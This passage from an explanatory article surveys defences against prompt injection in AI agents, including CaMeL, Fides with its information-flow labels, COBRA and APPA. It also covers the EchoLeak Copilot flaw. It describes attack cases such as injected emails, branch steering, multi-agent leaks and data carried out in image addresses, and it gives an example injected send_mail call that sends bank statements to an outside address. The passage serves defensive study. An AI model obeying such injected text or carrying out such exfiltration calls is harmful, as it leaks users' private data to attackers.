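The rows are not strictly comparable because the models, adaptations and sets of tasks differ. But the two GPT-5.2 rows isolate the effect of the policies, which blocked the one remaining attack and reduced the number of completed tasks by almost half. Garby and colleagues saw the same drop to 37.5% with another model, MiMo-v2.5, where the policies stopped four attacks that had succeeded without them.

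Stopping every attack on AgentDojo is only limited evidence that a defence is secure. Bhagwatkar and colleagues also did this with a filter, a language model that removes suspicious instructions from tool results, and GPT-4o still solved 74.1% of tasks. They concluded that the benchmark's attacks are too weak and that some of its scoring is faulty. By 2026, OpenAI's GPT-5.5 resisted all 949 cases with no defence. The case for CaMeL therefore rests on its structure. A filter that stops every attack in a fixed set may fail against an attacker who adapts to it, as Nasr, Carlini and colleagues found for most of the defences they studied. CaMeL's program is written before any injection is read, so rewording the injection does not add a line to it.

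### What the guarantee covers

CaMeL protects control-flow integrity by construction, which means untrusted text cannot introduce a tool call that the program does not contain. Garby and colleagues estimated how much this achieves by itself. Of the 144 pairs of task and attack in the banking environment, 97 need a tool call that would not normally appear in a program for the user's task. For example, an attacker cannot trigger a transfer if the user asked only for a summary of recent payments. In the other 47 pairs, the legitimate program already contains the calls the attacker needs, so protection depends on the values and the policies.

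The CaMeL paper, as quoted by Willison, acknowledges that users must write those policies and keep them up to date, and that frequent requests for approval wear people down. Strict rules also block legitimate work. *SPA* (Girrens and Wang, 2026) describes a related system that also plans first, then refuses any plan in which untrusted data drives a sensitive action. Turning that check on reduced the share of AgentDojo tasks solved from 53% to 29%, mainly because ordinary tasks often require an agent to act on outside information. CaMeL's policies can be more flexible because each tool has its own, but Girrens and Wang point out that the guarantee then depends on every policy being correct and complete.

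How much this protection reduces an agent's usefulness may depend on the design. Garby and colleagues built a banking agent in a small programming language and used a proof checker to prove that the language tracks data soundly. The agent's planning model can declare in advance that the program may trust a particular piece of outside data. With enforcement always on, the agent solved 75% of the banking tasks using GPT-5.2, and two of 1,296 attacks succeeded across three models. In both, the user had asked the agent to make a payment according to instructions in a file, and the attacker had replaced the file's contents. CaMeL's guarantees exclude this kind of attack, and tracking where data came from can't help when the user has told the agent to trust the source.

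CaMeL has more difficulty with tasks whose steps are in the untrusted text. If a user says "Do what the action items in Julia's email say", the planning model can't plan the steps because it can't read the email. It can ask the user, prepare branches for the likely cases, or write a program that reads an instruction and carries it out. When Garby and colleagues ran a banking task that said to follow a file's instructions, CaMeL's planning model wrote such a program, with a branch for each tool. The file's contents then determined which actions the program took, and with policies off, an injection succeeded without changing the program.

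Information can also leak through side channels. If a program sets a variable only when an account balance exceeds some amount, the variable reveals something about the balance even when that line does not run, but CaMeL's interpreter updates tags only on the branch it takes. Retries can leak information too. When a program fails, software outside the interpreter starts another attempt, and whether a policy blocked the previous one may depend on a secret. Each attempt can reveal one bit, so 14 well-chosen attempts would be enough to reveal a four-digit code, which holds about 13.3 bits. Both leaks are harder to exploit than an ordinary injection because an outsider cannot write such a program directly. Garby and colleagues also found a bug that removed an untrusted value's tag when the value was inserted into a piece of text.

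### Agents that instruct other agents

CaMeL's guarantee applies to one agent and its user. *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues, 2026) tested what happens when one CaMeL agent gives instructions to another. A coordinating agent received a request to send Julie a Slack message summarising job applicants. It got the records from a database agent, had its quarantined model summarise them, and told a messaging agent to send the summary, which it included in the text of the instruction.

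An attacker had planted an instruction in the database. Neither the coordinator nor the database agent changed its program, because neither planning model saw the records. But the messaging agent treated the whole sentence as its user's request. Its planning model read the planted instruction and wrote an extra line that emailed the applicants' details to an outside address. Peters-Gill and colleagues proved that, under mild assumptions, any such team with an untrusted data source can fail in this way, however well each member is protected.

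Their remedy splits each message between agents into an instruction and a set of named values. The receiving agent's planning model is given the instruction and the names, and the interpreter rejects any instruction that depends on a tool's output. On the 949 attack cases, adapted for teams of agents, the average success rate across five models was 12.9% without CaMeL, 0.2% when each agent was protected separately, and zero with the split messages. Policies were switched off in all of these runs, so the results measure only how well the plan was protected.

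In the experiments, CaMeL also reduced success rates less for stronger models. On a separate set of 112 industrial maintenance tasks, ordinary CaMeL lowered the success rate by 21.6 percentage points on average, but by 13.4 points for GPT-5.5 and Anthropic's Claude Fable 5, the two strongest models tested. Dividing the messages lowered the success rate for those two by less than one additional point. Part of the loss occurs because a program must specify how to parse a tool's output before anyone has seen it, so developers have to document the exact format of every result.

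### Computer use

Some agents operate a computer by looking at the screen and clicking. This is awkward for CaMeL, because the planning model is not allowed to see the screen. Policies are also hard to write, because the same click can open a preview or confirm a payment, depending on what is displayed.

*CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (Foerster, Blanchard and colleagues, 2026) adapts the design to computer use. The planning model writes a program that covers many possible screens, and a quarantined model that can read images reports which one has appeared. In a typical step, the program checks whether a cookie notice is visible and closes it if so. The programs average 41 tool calls and 40 branches, compared with about five and four for AgentDojo.

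On OSWorld, a benchmark of everyday computer tasks, Claude Sonnet 4.5 solved 109 automatically scored tasks without the defence. With the defence, it solved 31 of those tasks on the first attempt and 62 (57%) within five attempts. It used 1.88 times as many tokens with the defence as without it.

The many branches gave attackers a new target. Foerster and colleagues placed a fake cookie notice in an advertisement. The quarantined model returned the notice's position, and the program clicked there, which opened the attacker's website. They call this branch steering, because the attacker makes the program follow a branch that suits the attacker, without injecting an instruction or adding a step. Checking the page's underlying code stopped the attack for only some types of advertisement, and querying an additional model did not reliably solve the problem.

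*Securing Computer-Use Agents Against Branch Steering Attacks* (Zingrillo, Foerster and colleagues, October 2026) measured this weakness. Branch steering attacks succeeded in 65 of 74 cases against the computer-use version of CaMeL, and in 67 against an agent with no separation. That version of CaMeL ran without policies, so the result shows that a fixed plan alone gives little protection when an attacker can choose among its branches.

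Their own system, COBRA, restores policies in a form that suits clicking. Before the agent sees any page, the planning model lists the sites, operations and values the agent may use in each branch of the plan. The agent's traffic must then pass through programs called proxies, which check the web requests its clicks produce. These requests are easier to interpret than the clicks themselves. None of 199 attacks succeeded, and on the same tasks without attacks, COBRA's success rate was 97% of the earlier system's.

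This also gives an imperfect answer to the question of who writes the policies. When Zingrillo and colleagues compared the generated limits with limits they had written by hand, 28 of 30 sets gave the right decisions. Of the other two, one was too strict and one allowed an unauthorised operation. The method also needs a description of what each website can do. Without one, COBRA can only restrict which sites the agent contacts, and in another benchmark all 14 attacks that misused a permitted site succeeded. COBRA cannot judge whether the text of a permitted comment is offensive, and it does not check the mail a desktop program sends or the files it writes. It also reduces the number of tasks completed. Claude Sonnet 5 completed 51% of 361 computer tasks by itself and 39% when it filled both roles in COBRA, with up to five attempts at each task.

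### What a reviewer can check

An ordinary agent chooses each tool call after reading the result of the last one, so nobody can list its actions in advance. CaMeL writes its program before taking any action, and Foerster and colleagues note that a person can inspect or approve the program first. A reviewer of the invoice program can see that, whatever the mailbox contains, it sends one message and takes the recipient from the contact list. Longer programs are harder to review. The AgentDojo programs averaged 52 lines, but those for computer use averaged 213, and about half of their steps were fallbacks that a given run would not use.

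While the program runs, a monitor can record each call with its arguments and their origins. Software checks the policy before the call takes effect, so it can stop a forbidden transfer without waiting for a person. If the policy requires human approval, the reviewer can see that the program is about to send an invoice to an address it found in yesterday's email from a new contact. That is easier to judge than a bare request for permission to send mail.

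A record of where a value came from does not show that the value is true. *From Agent Traces to Trust* (Wang, Zhang and colleagues, 2026) distinguishes information that influenced an action from evidence that justified it, and a trace of the run may record only the information that influenced it. The paper also found that few systems report protecting their traces from later changes. In the invoice task, a genuine invoice and a forged one leave the same kind of record, because both came from the mailbox, were selected by the quarantined model and went to an approved recipient.

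## Fides: labels that follow data and block forbidden tool calls

In Fides (short for "Flow Integrity Deterministic Enforcement System"), an AI agent's data carries labels, and software checks them before every tool call. Costa, Köpf and colleagues developed it at Microsoft and describe it in *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (2025). CaMeL fixes its program before the agent opens any message, whereas an agent under Fides chooses each step after seeing the result of the last one. It can read untrusted text in full, but the labels then restrict what it can do for the rest of the run.

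Fides uses information-flow control, a technique decades older than AI agents. Ordinary access control determines who may open a file, while information-flow control also governs what happens to the contents when a program later copies them or combines them with other data.

### Labels and joins

The standard form of the technique comes from Denning's 1976 paper *A Lattice Model of Secure Information Flow*, which assigns every piece of data to a security class and specifies which classes information may flow between. When a program combines data from classes A and B, the result belongs to their join, written A ⊔ B, which is the least restrictive class that both may flow into. If the result had a looser class than one of its sources, anyone could remove a secret's restrictions by combining it with harmless data. Denning showed that under mild assumptions the classes form a lattice, an ordered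 set in which every pair has a join. She also showed that a sequence of operations is secure if each operation is secure by itself, so software can check one step at a time.

A label in Fides has two parts:

- Integrity is either trusted (T) or untrusted (U). The join of T and U is U, so anything derived partly from untrusted data is untrusted.
- Confidentiality is the set of people who may read the data. The join is the intersection of the sets. If Ann, Bob and Carol may read one document, and Bob, Carol and Dan may read another, only Bob and Carol may read a summary of both.

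The agent's context is everything the model has read so far. If the messages in it have labels ℓ₁ to ℓₖ, the context's label is their join, L = ℓ₁ ⊔ ℓ₂ ⊔ … ⊔ ℓₖ, and every tool call the model writes also gets the label L. This rule is deliberately cautious because nobody can be certain which parts of its input a model used.

Before each tool call, a policy engine compares the labels with the tool's policy. Two rules cover most cases:

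- Trusted action: a call with real consequences may run only if its context and its important arguments are trusted.
- Permitted flow: a call that sends data out may run only if every recipient belongs to the data's set of readers.

The permitted-flow rule does not stop prompt injection by itself, since a stranger could still make the agent send an unwanted message to someone allowed to read it. The trusted-action rule by itself lets the agent send private data to new readers, as long as no untrusted text influenced the decision. Security researchers call this property robust declassification, meaning that the user can share a document with new readers but an injected instruction can't.

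### The invoice request under Fides

Suppose the office assistant receives the request to find the invoice and send it to the accountant, and reads the search results directly. The context label changes as follows:

| What the model has read | Integrity | Who may read the context |
|---|---|---|
| The user's request | Trusted | Everyone |
| The supplier's email with the invoice | Untrusted | The user and the supplier |
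| The stranger's email | Untrusted | The user only |

The last row follows from the intersection {user, supplier} ∩ {user, stranger} = {user}. If the model obeys the stranger, it first fetches the bank statements, which the policy allows because reading them has no outside effect. Then it requests this call:

```
send_mail(to = outside_address, attachment = bank_statements)
```

The policy engine blocks the call. It breaks the trusted-action rule because the context is untrusted, and the permitted-flow rule because the outside address is not among the permitted readers of the bank statements. The harness reports the violation to the model as the result of the call, and the agent can try something else.

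The same check also blocks the call the user wanted, which would send the invoice to the accountant. The context is still untrusted, and the accountant was not a recipient of the supplier's email. Labels alone would protect the bank statements but also prevent the assistant from finishing the task.

Fides avoids this by hiding data in variables, as the dual-model pattern does, but it hides only the parts of a tool result whose labels are more restrictive than the context's. The rest stays visible, so the model might see an email's date but not its text. The quarantined model can answer questions about the hidden text, and its answers go into further variables:

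```
search_mail("invoice")                                  gives #mails
query_llm("Which message holds the invoice?", #mails)   gives #number
get_attachment(#mails, #number)                         gives #invoice
look_up_contact("accountant")                           gives the address
send_mail(to = address, attachment = #invoice)
```

The context never takes in untrusted text, so it is still trusted at the last line. The recipient comes from the contact list and is trusted too. Only the attachment is untrusted, which a sensible policy for sending mail allows. Under robust declassification, the user's request is also enough to let the accountant read the invoice. As with CaMeL, the stranger can still trick the quarantined model into choosing the wrong attachment.

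### Restricted answers and declassification

Hiding everything from the agent fails when its next step depends on what the text says. Costa and colleagues give the example of an agent that must read three emails and create a calendar event if one of them asks for a meeting.

Fides lets the quarantined model return an answer of a restricted type, such as yes or no. Software enforces the type while the model generates the answer, and the type becomes part of the label. Types are also ordered by how much information they can carry, from a yes/no answer to a choice from a list to free text. To add a calendar event, for example, the agent first reads a yes/no answer. If it is yes, the agent asks the quarantined model to extract the date, time and participants, and passes these to the calendar tool without reading them.

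The yes or no still comes from untrusted text, so a strict policy would block the calendar call. The developer has to write an exception that lets an untrusted yes or no influence an action, but not untrusted free text. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026) distinguishes two kinds of exception. Declassification permits a specified release of sensitive information, and endorsement treats selected untrusted data as trusted for a defined purpose. Accepting the answer about the meeting is an endorsement. A stranger can exploit it to create a false appointment but can't use it to pass along an instruction, because the answer is only one bit.

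Like CaMeL's tags, labels miss information that leaks through a program's choices, which Denning called an implicit flow. For instance, an agent creates one if it sends a harmless reminder only when a private balance is low. Costa and colleagues proved that their method can block explicit flows, in which the data itself goes into an outgoing call. They chose not to block implicit flows because that would essentially stop an agent from doing anything publicly visible after reading private data.

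### Results on AgentDojo

Costa and colleagues tested Fides on AgentDojo's 97 tasks using GPT-4o. With policies off, 152 attacks succeeded against an ordinary agent and 21 against Fides. With policies on, none succeeded against either. AgentDojo's scoring counted a few more successes, including some in which the policy had blocked the harmful call. The zero result is partly due to how they assigned labels. They marked a data field as untrusted whenever at least one AgentDojo attack used it, but a company labelling its own data doesn't have a list of the fields attackers will use.

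Policies cost the ordinary agent much more than they cost Fides:

| Tasks completed without an attack | Workspace | Travel | Banking | Slack |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Ordinary agent, no policies | 75.0% | 70.0% | 98.8% | 93.3% |
| Ordinary agent with labels and policies | 37.0% | 73.0% | 37.5% | 20.0% |
| Fides, policies off | 63.5% | 50.0% | 65.0% | 63.8% |
| Fides, policies on | 59.0% | 41.0% | 52.5% | 47.6% |

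With policies on, Fides completed about 8 percentage points more tasks on average than the ordinary agent, and 16 points more when both used OpenAI's o1 reasoning model. Fides did worse in the travel environment because many travel tools are allowed to run in an untrusted context anyway, and GPT-4o often mishandled the variables. With o1, Fides's travel score rose from 41% to 68%.

Costa and colleagues also sorted the 97 tasks by how much the agent has to see. An agent can complete 26 of them by passing variables from one tool to the next. Another 51 need the quarantined model to process some text, but the sequence of tool calls doesn't depend on what the text contains. In the remaining 20, the right sequence depends on the data. Most of these are in banking and Slack, where a typical task is to read a file and follow its instructions. Reading the file makes the context untrusted, so the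 policy correctly blocks the payment that would follow. The restricted answers could help with some of these tasks, but Costa and colleagues left them out of the tests because few AgentDojo tasks needed them.

Some results were due to luck. One banking task asks the agent to change the user's password if it finds a suspicious transaction. The transaction descriptions were hidden in variables, so the model judged by the amounts alone, picked out a large payment and changed the password. The benchmark counted this as a success.

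### Label creep

In the invoice example, a single email from a stranger made the whole context untrusted and left the user as its only permitted reader. Labels become more restrictive as an agent reads and never relax by themselves, so by the end of a long run the policy can block nearly everything. Researchers call this label creep. In the extreme case, all data carries every label, so the labels no longer distinguish anything.

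In *The Limits of Information-Flow Control Enforcement for Agentic Systems*, Gregory, Domico and colleagues (2026) measured how far the arrangement of a team of agents can reduce label creep before declassification becomes necessary. They used a simulation without a language model. In the main experiments, each task has 20 tool calls, some of which depend on the results of others. The simulator distributes the calls among five agents, marks some of the calls as sensitive and passes results along the links between agents. An agent that handles sensitive data, even just to forward it, keeps the sensitive label for the rest of the task.

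The study compared ten arrangements of agents. In a mesh, every agent is linked to every other, and in a ring, each agent has two neighbours. In a star, all data goes through a central agent, while in a hierarchy it goes through managers. Five more arrangements were random networks, and the last was an ideal network with exactly the direct links the task requires. Gregory and colleagues measured lost usefulness as the share of tool calls that either introduce sensitive data or run under a sensitive label. Excess loss is how much more usefulness an arrangement loses than the ideal network.

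With four sensitive calls out of 20, the excess loss was about 5 percentage points for the star, 4 for the hierarchy and 3 for the ring. The mesh matched the ideal network. In a star, the central agent acquires the sensitive label as soon as it forwards one private result, and then spreads it to agents that had no need of that result. Across the nine fixed arrangements, lost usefulness had a correlation of −0.96 with density, the share of possible links that exist. (This is a rank correlation, so it shows that denser networks almost always lost less, but not how much less.)

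Dividing the work among more agents also reduced the loss, because each agent's context isolates what it has read. But more agents also means more links to monitor. A mesh of n agents has n(n − 1)/2 links, which is 10 for five agents and 190 for 20. Gregory and colleagues suggest sparser random networks as a compromise, including one design with an expected 70% fewer links than a mesh. However, the five-agent network they drew from that design happened to have 7 of the 10 possible links, so its good result is weak evidence about how sparse networks perform. Giving the sensitive tools to a few dedicated agents reduced the loss in every arrangement.

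Even the ideal network lost usefulness, and Gregory and colleagues conclude that agents also need declassification. But their simulation has no declassification, hidden variables or fresh contexts, so it cannot show how much usefulness a system like Fides would lose. It also counts tool calls that run under a sensitive label, many of which a real policy would allow. And because the simulation doesn't run a model, it cannot show whether an agent would have found another way to finish the task.

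### Tracking only the data that mattered

To reduce label creep, *RTBAS* (Zhong, Chen and colleagues, 2025) adds a screener that picks out the parts of the context relevant to the next tool call, instead of assuming that the whole context influenced it. The system joins the labels of only those parts, then masks anything whose label is more restrictive than the result before the model writes the call. If the screener wrongly leaves out restricted data, the model cannot see it, so the mistake may spoil the task but cannot leak the data. The screener can be a second language model or a small neural network trained on attention scores, which estimate how strongly each part of the input affected the output.

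RTBAS stopped every AgentDojo attack that violated its policies. In one further case, the injected text was in something the user had apparently written, which carried a trusted label. Under attack, the number of completed tasks fell by less than 1% with the language-model screener and by 3% with the attention-based one. Without attacks, it fell by 10% and 7.4%. These figures are averages, and the agent did poorly in the Slack environment, completing only 22% of tasks with the language-model screener and 33% with the attention-based one, because many of the tasks require it to act on text from an untrusted website.

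Zhong and colleagues also wrote 37 tasks involving private data in payments, flight booking and shopping. A system that asks the user to confirm every tool call asked needlessly in 29.7% of cases, compared with 8.1% for RTBAS with the language-model screener. RTBAS failed to ask when it should have in 10.8% of cases, typically because it had masked private data that the task required. On AgentDojo's banking tasks, RTBAS also raised the cost per task from 1.5 to 3.2 cents and the running time from 4.4 to 9.7 seconds.

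Later methods estimate influence more precisely. *GIF* (2026) calculates how strongly each labelled piece of text affects an output, then asks a language model whether that influence is harmful. *Information Flow Control* (2026), a summary by DAPLab, the Columbia University lab that developed GIF, reports that this matches or beats using GPT-5.5 as the judge, at up to 81 times lower token cost. *Sightline* (2026) removed 50% of label creep in its tests, with a miss rate of 3.9% per episode. Removing a label is riskier than masking the text because the model has already seen the data, so a tracker that wrongly decides the data did not matter can let a forbidden flow through.

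### Recovering from a blocked call

*APPA* (Kravchenko, Liventsev and colleagues, 2026) keeps the cautious joins but changes what happens after a refusal. When a call fails its check, the system lists steps that could make the call allowable. The agent might have to complete a missing prerequisite, remove secrets with an approved tool, or get permission from a designated person or program. That permission covers only one exact call and leaves the labels unchanged, so an attacker cannot reuse it for another recipient.

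The agent can also read untrusted material in a temporary branch. For example, a support agent that needs information from a public web page starts a copy of itself with the current context and label. The copy reads the page and may return only a ticket number, a severity level and the name of a component, each in a fixed format. The system then discards the copy and everything it read, but this does not undo anything the copy did in the outside world. A malicious page can still make the copy return the wrong severity, and the developer has to decide whether to treat the returned values as trusted.

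APPA also accounts for data that a tool reads during the call. Suppose one tool reads a confidential ledger and emails it in a single call. The context may contain no confidential data just before the call, so a check on its existing label would approve it. APPA adds the label of the data the tool will read, and checks the combined label before the tool runs.

Kravchenko and colleagues compared APPA with two configurations of Fides, built from Microsoft's software, on 20 simulated corporate tasks. Across three models, APPA completed 87–91% of runs and no attack succeeded. The Fides configurations completed 36–46% of runs, and 26–35% of attacks against them succeeded. The comparison favours APPA because its developers wrote the benchmark and both Fides configurations, and the Fides policies did not cover several rules that the tasks tested, such as sending a document exactly once. On AgentThreatBench,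 an independent benchmark of 24 tasks, APPA again stopped every attack but completed only 64–77% of runs. With one of the three models, both Fides configurations completed more runs than APPA, though some attacks against them succeeded.

Tests that remove parts of APPA give better evidence of what its recovery features achieve. With one model, the agent completed 88% of the corporate runs with the full system, 56.5% without branches and 35% without the lists of remedies. No attack succeeded against any of these versions.

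### Planning around the policy

An agent that does not know the rules can make its own context untrusted unnecessarily, for instance by opening an email that it could have passed along in a variable. *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues, 2026) introduces Prudentia, a version of Fides that tells the model the labels and each tool's policy. Before opening a variable, the model must explain why it needs to and list the tool calls it plans to make afterwards. The policy engine still decides whether to allow each call, so a bad plan leads to extra questions or an unfinished task, but not to a forbidden call.

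Prudentia can also ask the user to endorse a piece of data. Suppose an email lists ten tasks. If the agent reads it without endorsement, the context becomes untrusted and the user has to approve each of the ten actions. If the user endorses the email first, they only have to approve once. Kolluri and colleagues did not offer a similar option for confidential data, because whether sharing it is appropriate depends on the recipient and occasion.

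Earlier comparisons ignored how often each agent has to ask a person. They tested protected agents that could ask nobody against unprotected ones that, in a real product, would have needed approval for every important action. A later comparison counted the questions. On AgentDojo with OpenAI's o3-mini, an ordinary agent that asks before every consequential action completed 24.3% of tasks without asking any questions. Adding labels raised this to 35.5%, while Fides reached 50.1% and Prudentia 59.1%. With o4-mini, Prudentia asked about 19 questions over the whole benchmark and Fides about 37, though Prudentia completed slightly fewer tasks (73.2% compared with 75.7%).

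The experiments assumed that users answer correctly. Endorsement makes each answer matter more, because a user who approves the ten-item list without noticing that a stranger added the seventh item also approves that action.

### Fides in Microsoft's software

Microsoft released Fides in May 2026 as an experimental part of its Agent Framework, a toolkit for building agents. Microsoft's *Stop prompt injection from hijacking your agent* (2026) acknowledges several limits. The software treats data from an unlabelled tool as trusted and public, so a forgotten label silently removes the protection. APPA instead marks such data as unknown and blocks sensitive calls until something establishes its label. In Microsoft's version, once untrusted text enters the context, the rest of the run is untrusted unless the developer explicitly removes the text. To avoid this, the software hides untrusted results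 in variables by default. Microsoft recommends Fides for agents that combine outside content with powerful tools, and ordinary tool calling for agents whose worst outcome is a wrong answer.

In June 2026, Microsoft's *Information-flow control* described further prototypes, including an optional feature in GitHub Copilot CLI, a coding agent that runs in a terminal. The feature did not yet cover all tools. To add a new service through Microsoft's experimental gateway, a developer has to describe the format of each tool's results, write a function that assigns labels to them, and write or choose a policy.

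The same article shows that labels can prevent leaks when nobody is attacking. In its example, Alex asks an agent to answer his unanswered email. Priya has sent him a preview of the quarterly sales, and Marco, who is not allowed to see the figures yet, has written to ask about them. Once the agent has read both messages, only Alex may read what it writes, because he is the only person allowed to read both ({Alex, Priya} ∩ {Alex, Marco} = {Alex}). The policy therefore holds the reply to Marco until Alex has reviewed it. If Priya had copied Marco in on her email, the agent could have replied without his review.

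Agent Framework records the labels and the policy decision for every call, which gives a monitor more information than a list of tool names. When a call needs a person's approval, the dialog can show where the untrusted text came from or who would gain access to the data. Microsoft says the framework's approval requests are still coarse and do not yet show the user all the labels behind a decision.

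## EchoLeak: data leaving through links and images

EchoLeak was a flaw in Microsoft 365 Copilot, the AI assistant in Microsoft's office software. It let an outsider obtain a company's private data by sending an email, without anyone clicking on anything. The data left because the program that displayed Copilot's reply automatically loaded an image whose web address contained the data. *EchoLeak* (Reddy and Gujral, 2025) points out that Copilot could not send email by itself.

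### Discovery and repair

Researchers at the AI security company Aim Security spent about three months working out how Copilot operated and reported the flaw to Microsoft in January 2025. *New Microsoft Copilot flaw signals broader risk of AI agents being hacked* (Goldman, 2025) reports that Microsoft attempted a fix in April but found further problems in May. Reddy and Gujral write that Microsoft fully repaired the flaw on its own servers in May. Microsoft and Aim Security made the flaw public on June 11. Adir Gruss, a co-founder of Aim Security, told Goldman that the repair took five months, which he considered very long. It took that long partly because this kind of flaw was so new that involving the right teams at Microsoft and explaining it to them took time.

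The flaw is listed in the public catalogue of software vulnerabilities as CVE-2025-32711. In its notice, reproduced in exploitDog's *CVE-2025-32711* (2025), Microsoft rated the severity at 9.3 out of 10, recorded no exploitation, and told customers they did not need to do anything. The US National Vulnerability Database scored it 7.5, according to *Compositional Threat Analysis of Latent Compromise in LLM Agent Systems* (2026). Microsoft also told Goldman that the flaw had not affected any customers.

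Goldman describes EchoLeak as the first known zero-click attack on an AI agent, but the route it used was already known. Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper* describes a zero-click leak of this kind that its author reported to OpenAI and Microsoft in early 2023. Microsoft responded that May by blocking most images in Bing Chat, an earlier assistant.

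### How the data left

In general terms, the attack had four steps:

1. An outsider sends an employee an email that looks like ordinary business correspondence but contains instructions for the assistant.
2. The employee later asks Copilot a question about work. Copilot searches for relevant material and puts the outsider's email in the same context as private files.
3. The model follows the email's instructions and writes a reply that includes an image address containing private details.
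4. The program showing the reply requests the image, which delivers the address and the details in it to the outsider's server.

"Zero-click" means the employee does not have to open the email or follow a link, but they do have to use Copilot. They would probably notice nothing more than a broken image.

Gruss considers the mixing in the second step the basic design flaw, and CaMeL and Fides address this problem. The fourth step is a separate weakness that turned a reply meant only for the employee into a message to an outsider. An agent's output therefore includes whatever other software does automatically with its text. A developer who lists only the agent's tools will miss the chat window, the mail program and any other software that displays or processes its replies.

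The same thing can happen in messaging apps, many of which fetch any linked page as soon as a message arrives so they can show a preview. The security company PromptArmor found that this could leak data from an agent's messages without anyone clicking the link, and that OpenClaw was exposed by default when people used it through Telegram.

In another case, Microsoft's Copilot Cowork let agents send email to the user's own inbox without approval. Willison (2026) reports that images in those messages could leak data when the user viewed them, even though the messages were addressed only to the user. The permitted-flow rule in Fides would also allow such a message if it counted only the user as a recipient. To prevent the leak, the rule must also count the server that supplies the image.

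### How much a web address can carry

Loading an image or opening a page is usually a "read-only" request, which means that it doesn't change anything on the website. But the website has to receive the requested address to answer, and OpenAI's *Keeping your data safse when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) notes that websites commonly log these addresses. An agent that is allowed to read any website can therefore also send messages to any website's owner by putting them in the addresses it requests.

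Often the user wants this to happen. Suppose an agent looks up the weather at this address:

```
https://weather.example/forecast?town=Leeds
```

The address has 43 characters. The first 38 identify the site and page, and from the last five the site's owner can learn which town the user is interested in. If the software accepts addresses of up to 2,000 characters, the part after "town=" can be 1,962 characters, enough for roughly 300 words of English.

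If each of those characters can be any of 64 letters, digits and symbols, it carries 6 bits, so the address can carry 11,772 bits in addition to its fixed part, compared with one bit for a yes/no answer from an Oracle. A 32-byte encryption key would fit into 43 characters, and a 100-kilobyte bank statement would take 68 addresses. The request itself delivers the data, so the website doesn't have to return anything useful.

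### Blocking automatic loading

The simplest fix is to stop the display program from loading anything automatically. This closes the route that EchoLeak used, however the attacker words the email, but users lose link previews and pictures in replies.

It does not stop leaks through links that the user clicks or through web pages that the agent opens with its own tools. The developer also has to apply it in every program that displays the agent's text. According to Embrace The Red, OpenAI introduced an early check on image addresses in December 2023, but at first left it out of ChatGPT's apps for Mac and iPhone.

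Developers can also remove images and links before the model reads them. Reddy and Gujral report that Microsoft now does this with embedded images and some links in material from outside a company. They also mention reports of an option that stops Copilot from using outside messages in certain contexts. This option makes an injection less likely to reach the model, but Copilot may then be unable to answer a question that depends on a customer's email.

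### Restricting destinations

A less drastic fix is to let the display program load images only from an allowlist of sites. Web pages can include such a list, called a content security policy, and the browser then blocks images from all other sites.

Copilot already had a list of this kind when Aim Security found EchoLeak, and the browser enforced it correctly. But one of the permitted Microsoft services would fetch outside addresses on request, so the browser contacted only that service, which then contacted the outside address. A year later, the security company Varonis found a similar Copilot flaw, SearchLeak. It required one click on a genuine Microsoft link, after which the data left through image requests made by Microsoft's search engine, Bing. Microsoft has patched the flaw, and there was no public evidence of attacks when Varonis disclosed it, according to WinBuzzer's *Microsoft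 Patches Copilot SearchLeak Data-Theft Flaw* (2026).

An allowlist therefore has to account for everything a permitted site will do with a request. OpenAI gives the example of a trusted site that immediately redirects the visitor to another site. A check of only the first address would miss this. Reddy and Gujral recommend sending permitted requests through an internal proxy that limits redirects and fetches only images whose addresses carry a valid, time-limited signature.

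Strict lists also inconvenience people who use many websites, and frequent warnings about harmless sites lead to careless approvals, as OpenAI points out.

### OpenAI's link check

In January 2026, OpenAI described a way to check whether an exact web address is already public, rather than whether its site is trustworthy. A crawler, a program that explores the public web, records the addresses it finds. It has no access to anyone's conversations or accounts. Before ChatGPT loads an address by itself, software looks for an exact match in these records. If there is one, ChatGPT may load the page or image. Otherwise, the software either has ChatGPT try another site or warns the user.

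This works because an address that the crawler found independently is unlikely to contain a secret from the user's conversation. The crawler may well have recorded the address of the forecast page for Leeds, but not one with a sentence from the user's mail in place of the town.

Some information can still get out, because the site's owner can see which of several known pages the agent opened. As with an Oracle's list of answers, a choice among 1,024 pages carries at most 10 bits. This is less than a thousandth of what the 2,000-character address could carry, but repeated visits can leak more. Embrace The Red suggests storing pages for a few minutes or refusing repeat visits to the same address within a session, which would make such leaks slower and harder to arrange. The check also doesn't block false or harmful content on a public page.

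Users lose some convenience when a legitimate address is unique. A supplier may email a private link for each invoice, and a crawler should never have seen those links, so the office assistant would need the user's permission to open them. OpenAI says it also requests confirmation for every link to sites that ask it not to catalogue them. The check thus still depends partly on users reading warnings. OpenAI's *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (2026) says the warning can show the information that would be sent, which gives the user something specific to judge.

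By March 2026, the check also covered page visits in OpenAI's Atlas browser and searches in Deep Research, a ChatGPT feature that compiles reports from many sources. OpenAI still listed protection against leaks through web addresses among ChatGPT's safeguards in early December. However, the check protects only the requests that pass through it, and Check Point Research's *ChatGPT Data Leakage via a Hidden Outbound Channel* (2026) describes a separate path to the internet from the environment where ChatGPT runs code.

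### Lockdown Mode

In February 2026, OpenAI introduced Lockdown Mode for organisations, an optional ChatGPT setting that restricts outgoing requests. It began extending the setting to personal accounts in June. According to OpenAI's *Introducing Lockdown Mode and Elevated Risk labels in ChatGPT* (2026), the agent can read only stored copies of web pages, so browsing sends no live requests outside OpenAI's network. The owner of a page cannot see that the agent has read it, which also closes the small channel that the link check leaves open.

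The cost to users is considerable. OpenAI's *Lockdown Mode* lists the restrictions as they stood in early December 2026:

- Search results may be out of date or missing.
- ChatGPT may not show images in ordinary replies, though users can still upload and generate them.
- Deep Research and Agent Mode, in which ChatGPT carries out tasks on the web, are unavailable.
- ChatGPT can't download files for analysis, and code written in its Canvas editor can't use the network.

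How Lockdown Mode treats connected apps depends on the type of account. On personal accounts, it blocks apps from accessing outside services live or changing anything in them when doing so would conflict with its protections. In larger organisations, administrators decide which apps and actions to allow. OpenAI advises them against enabling actions whose effects an outsider might see, even in apps they trust. For the invoice task, an administrator would have to decide whether the assistant may send mail at all, because an attacker could see a message sent to them.

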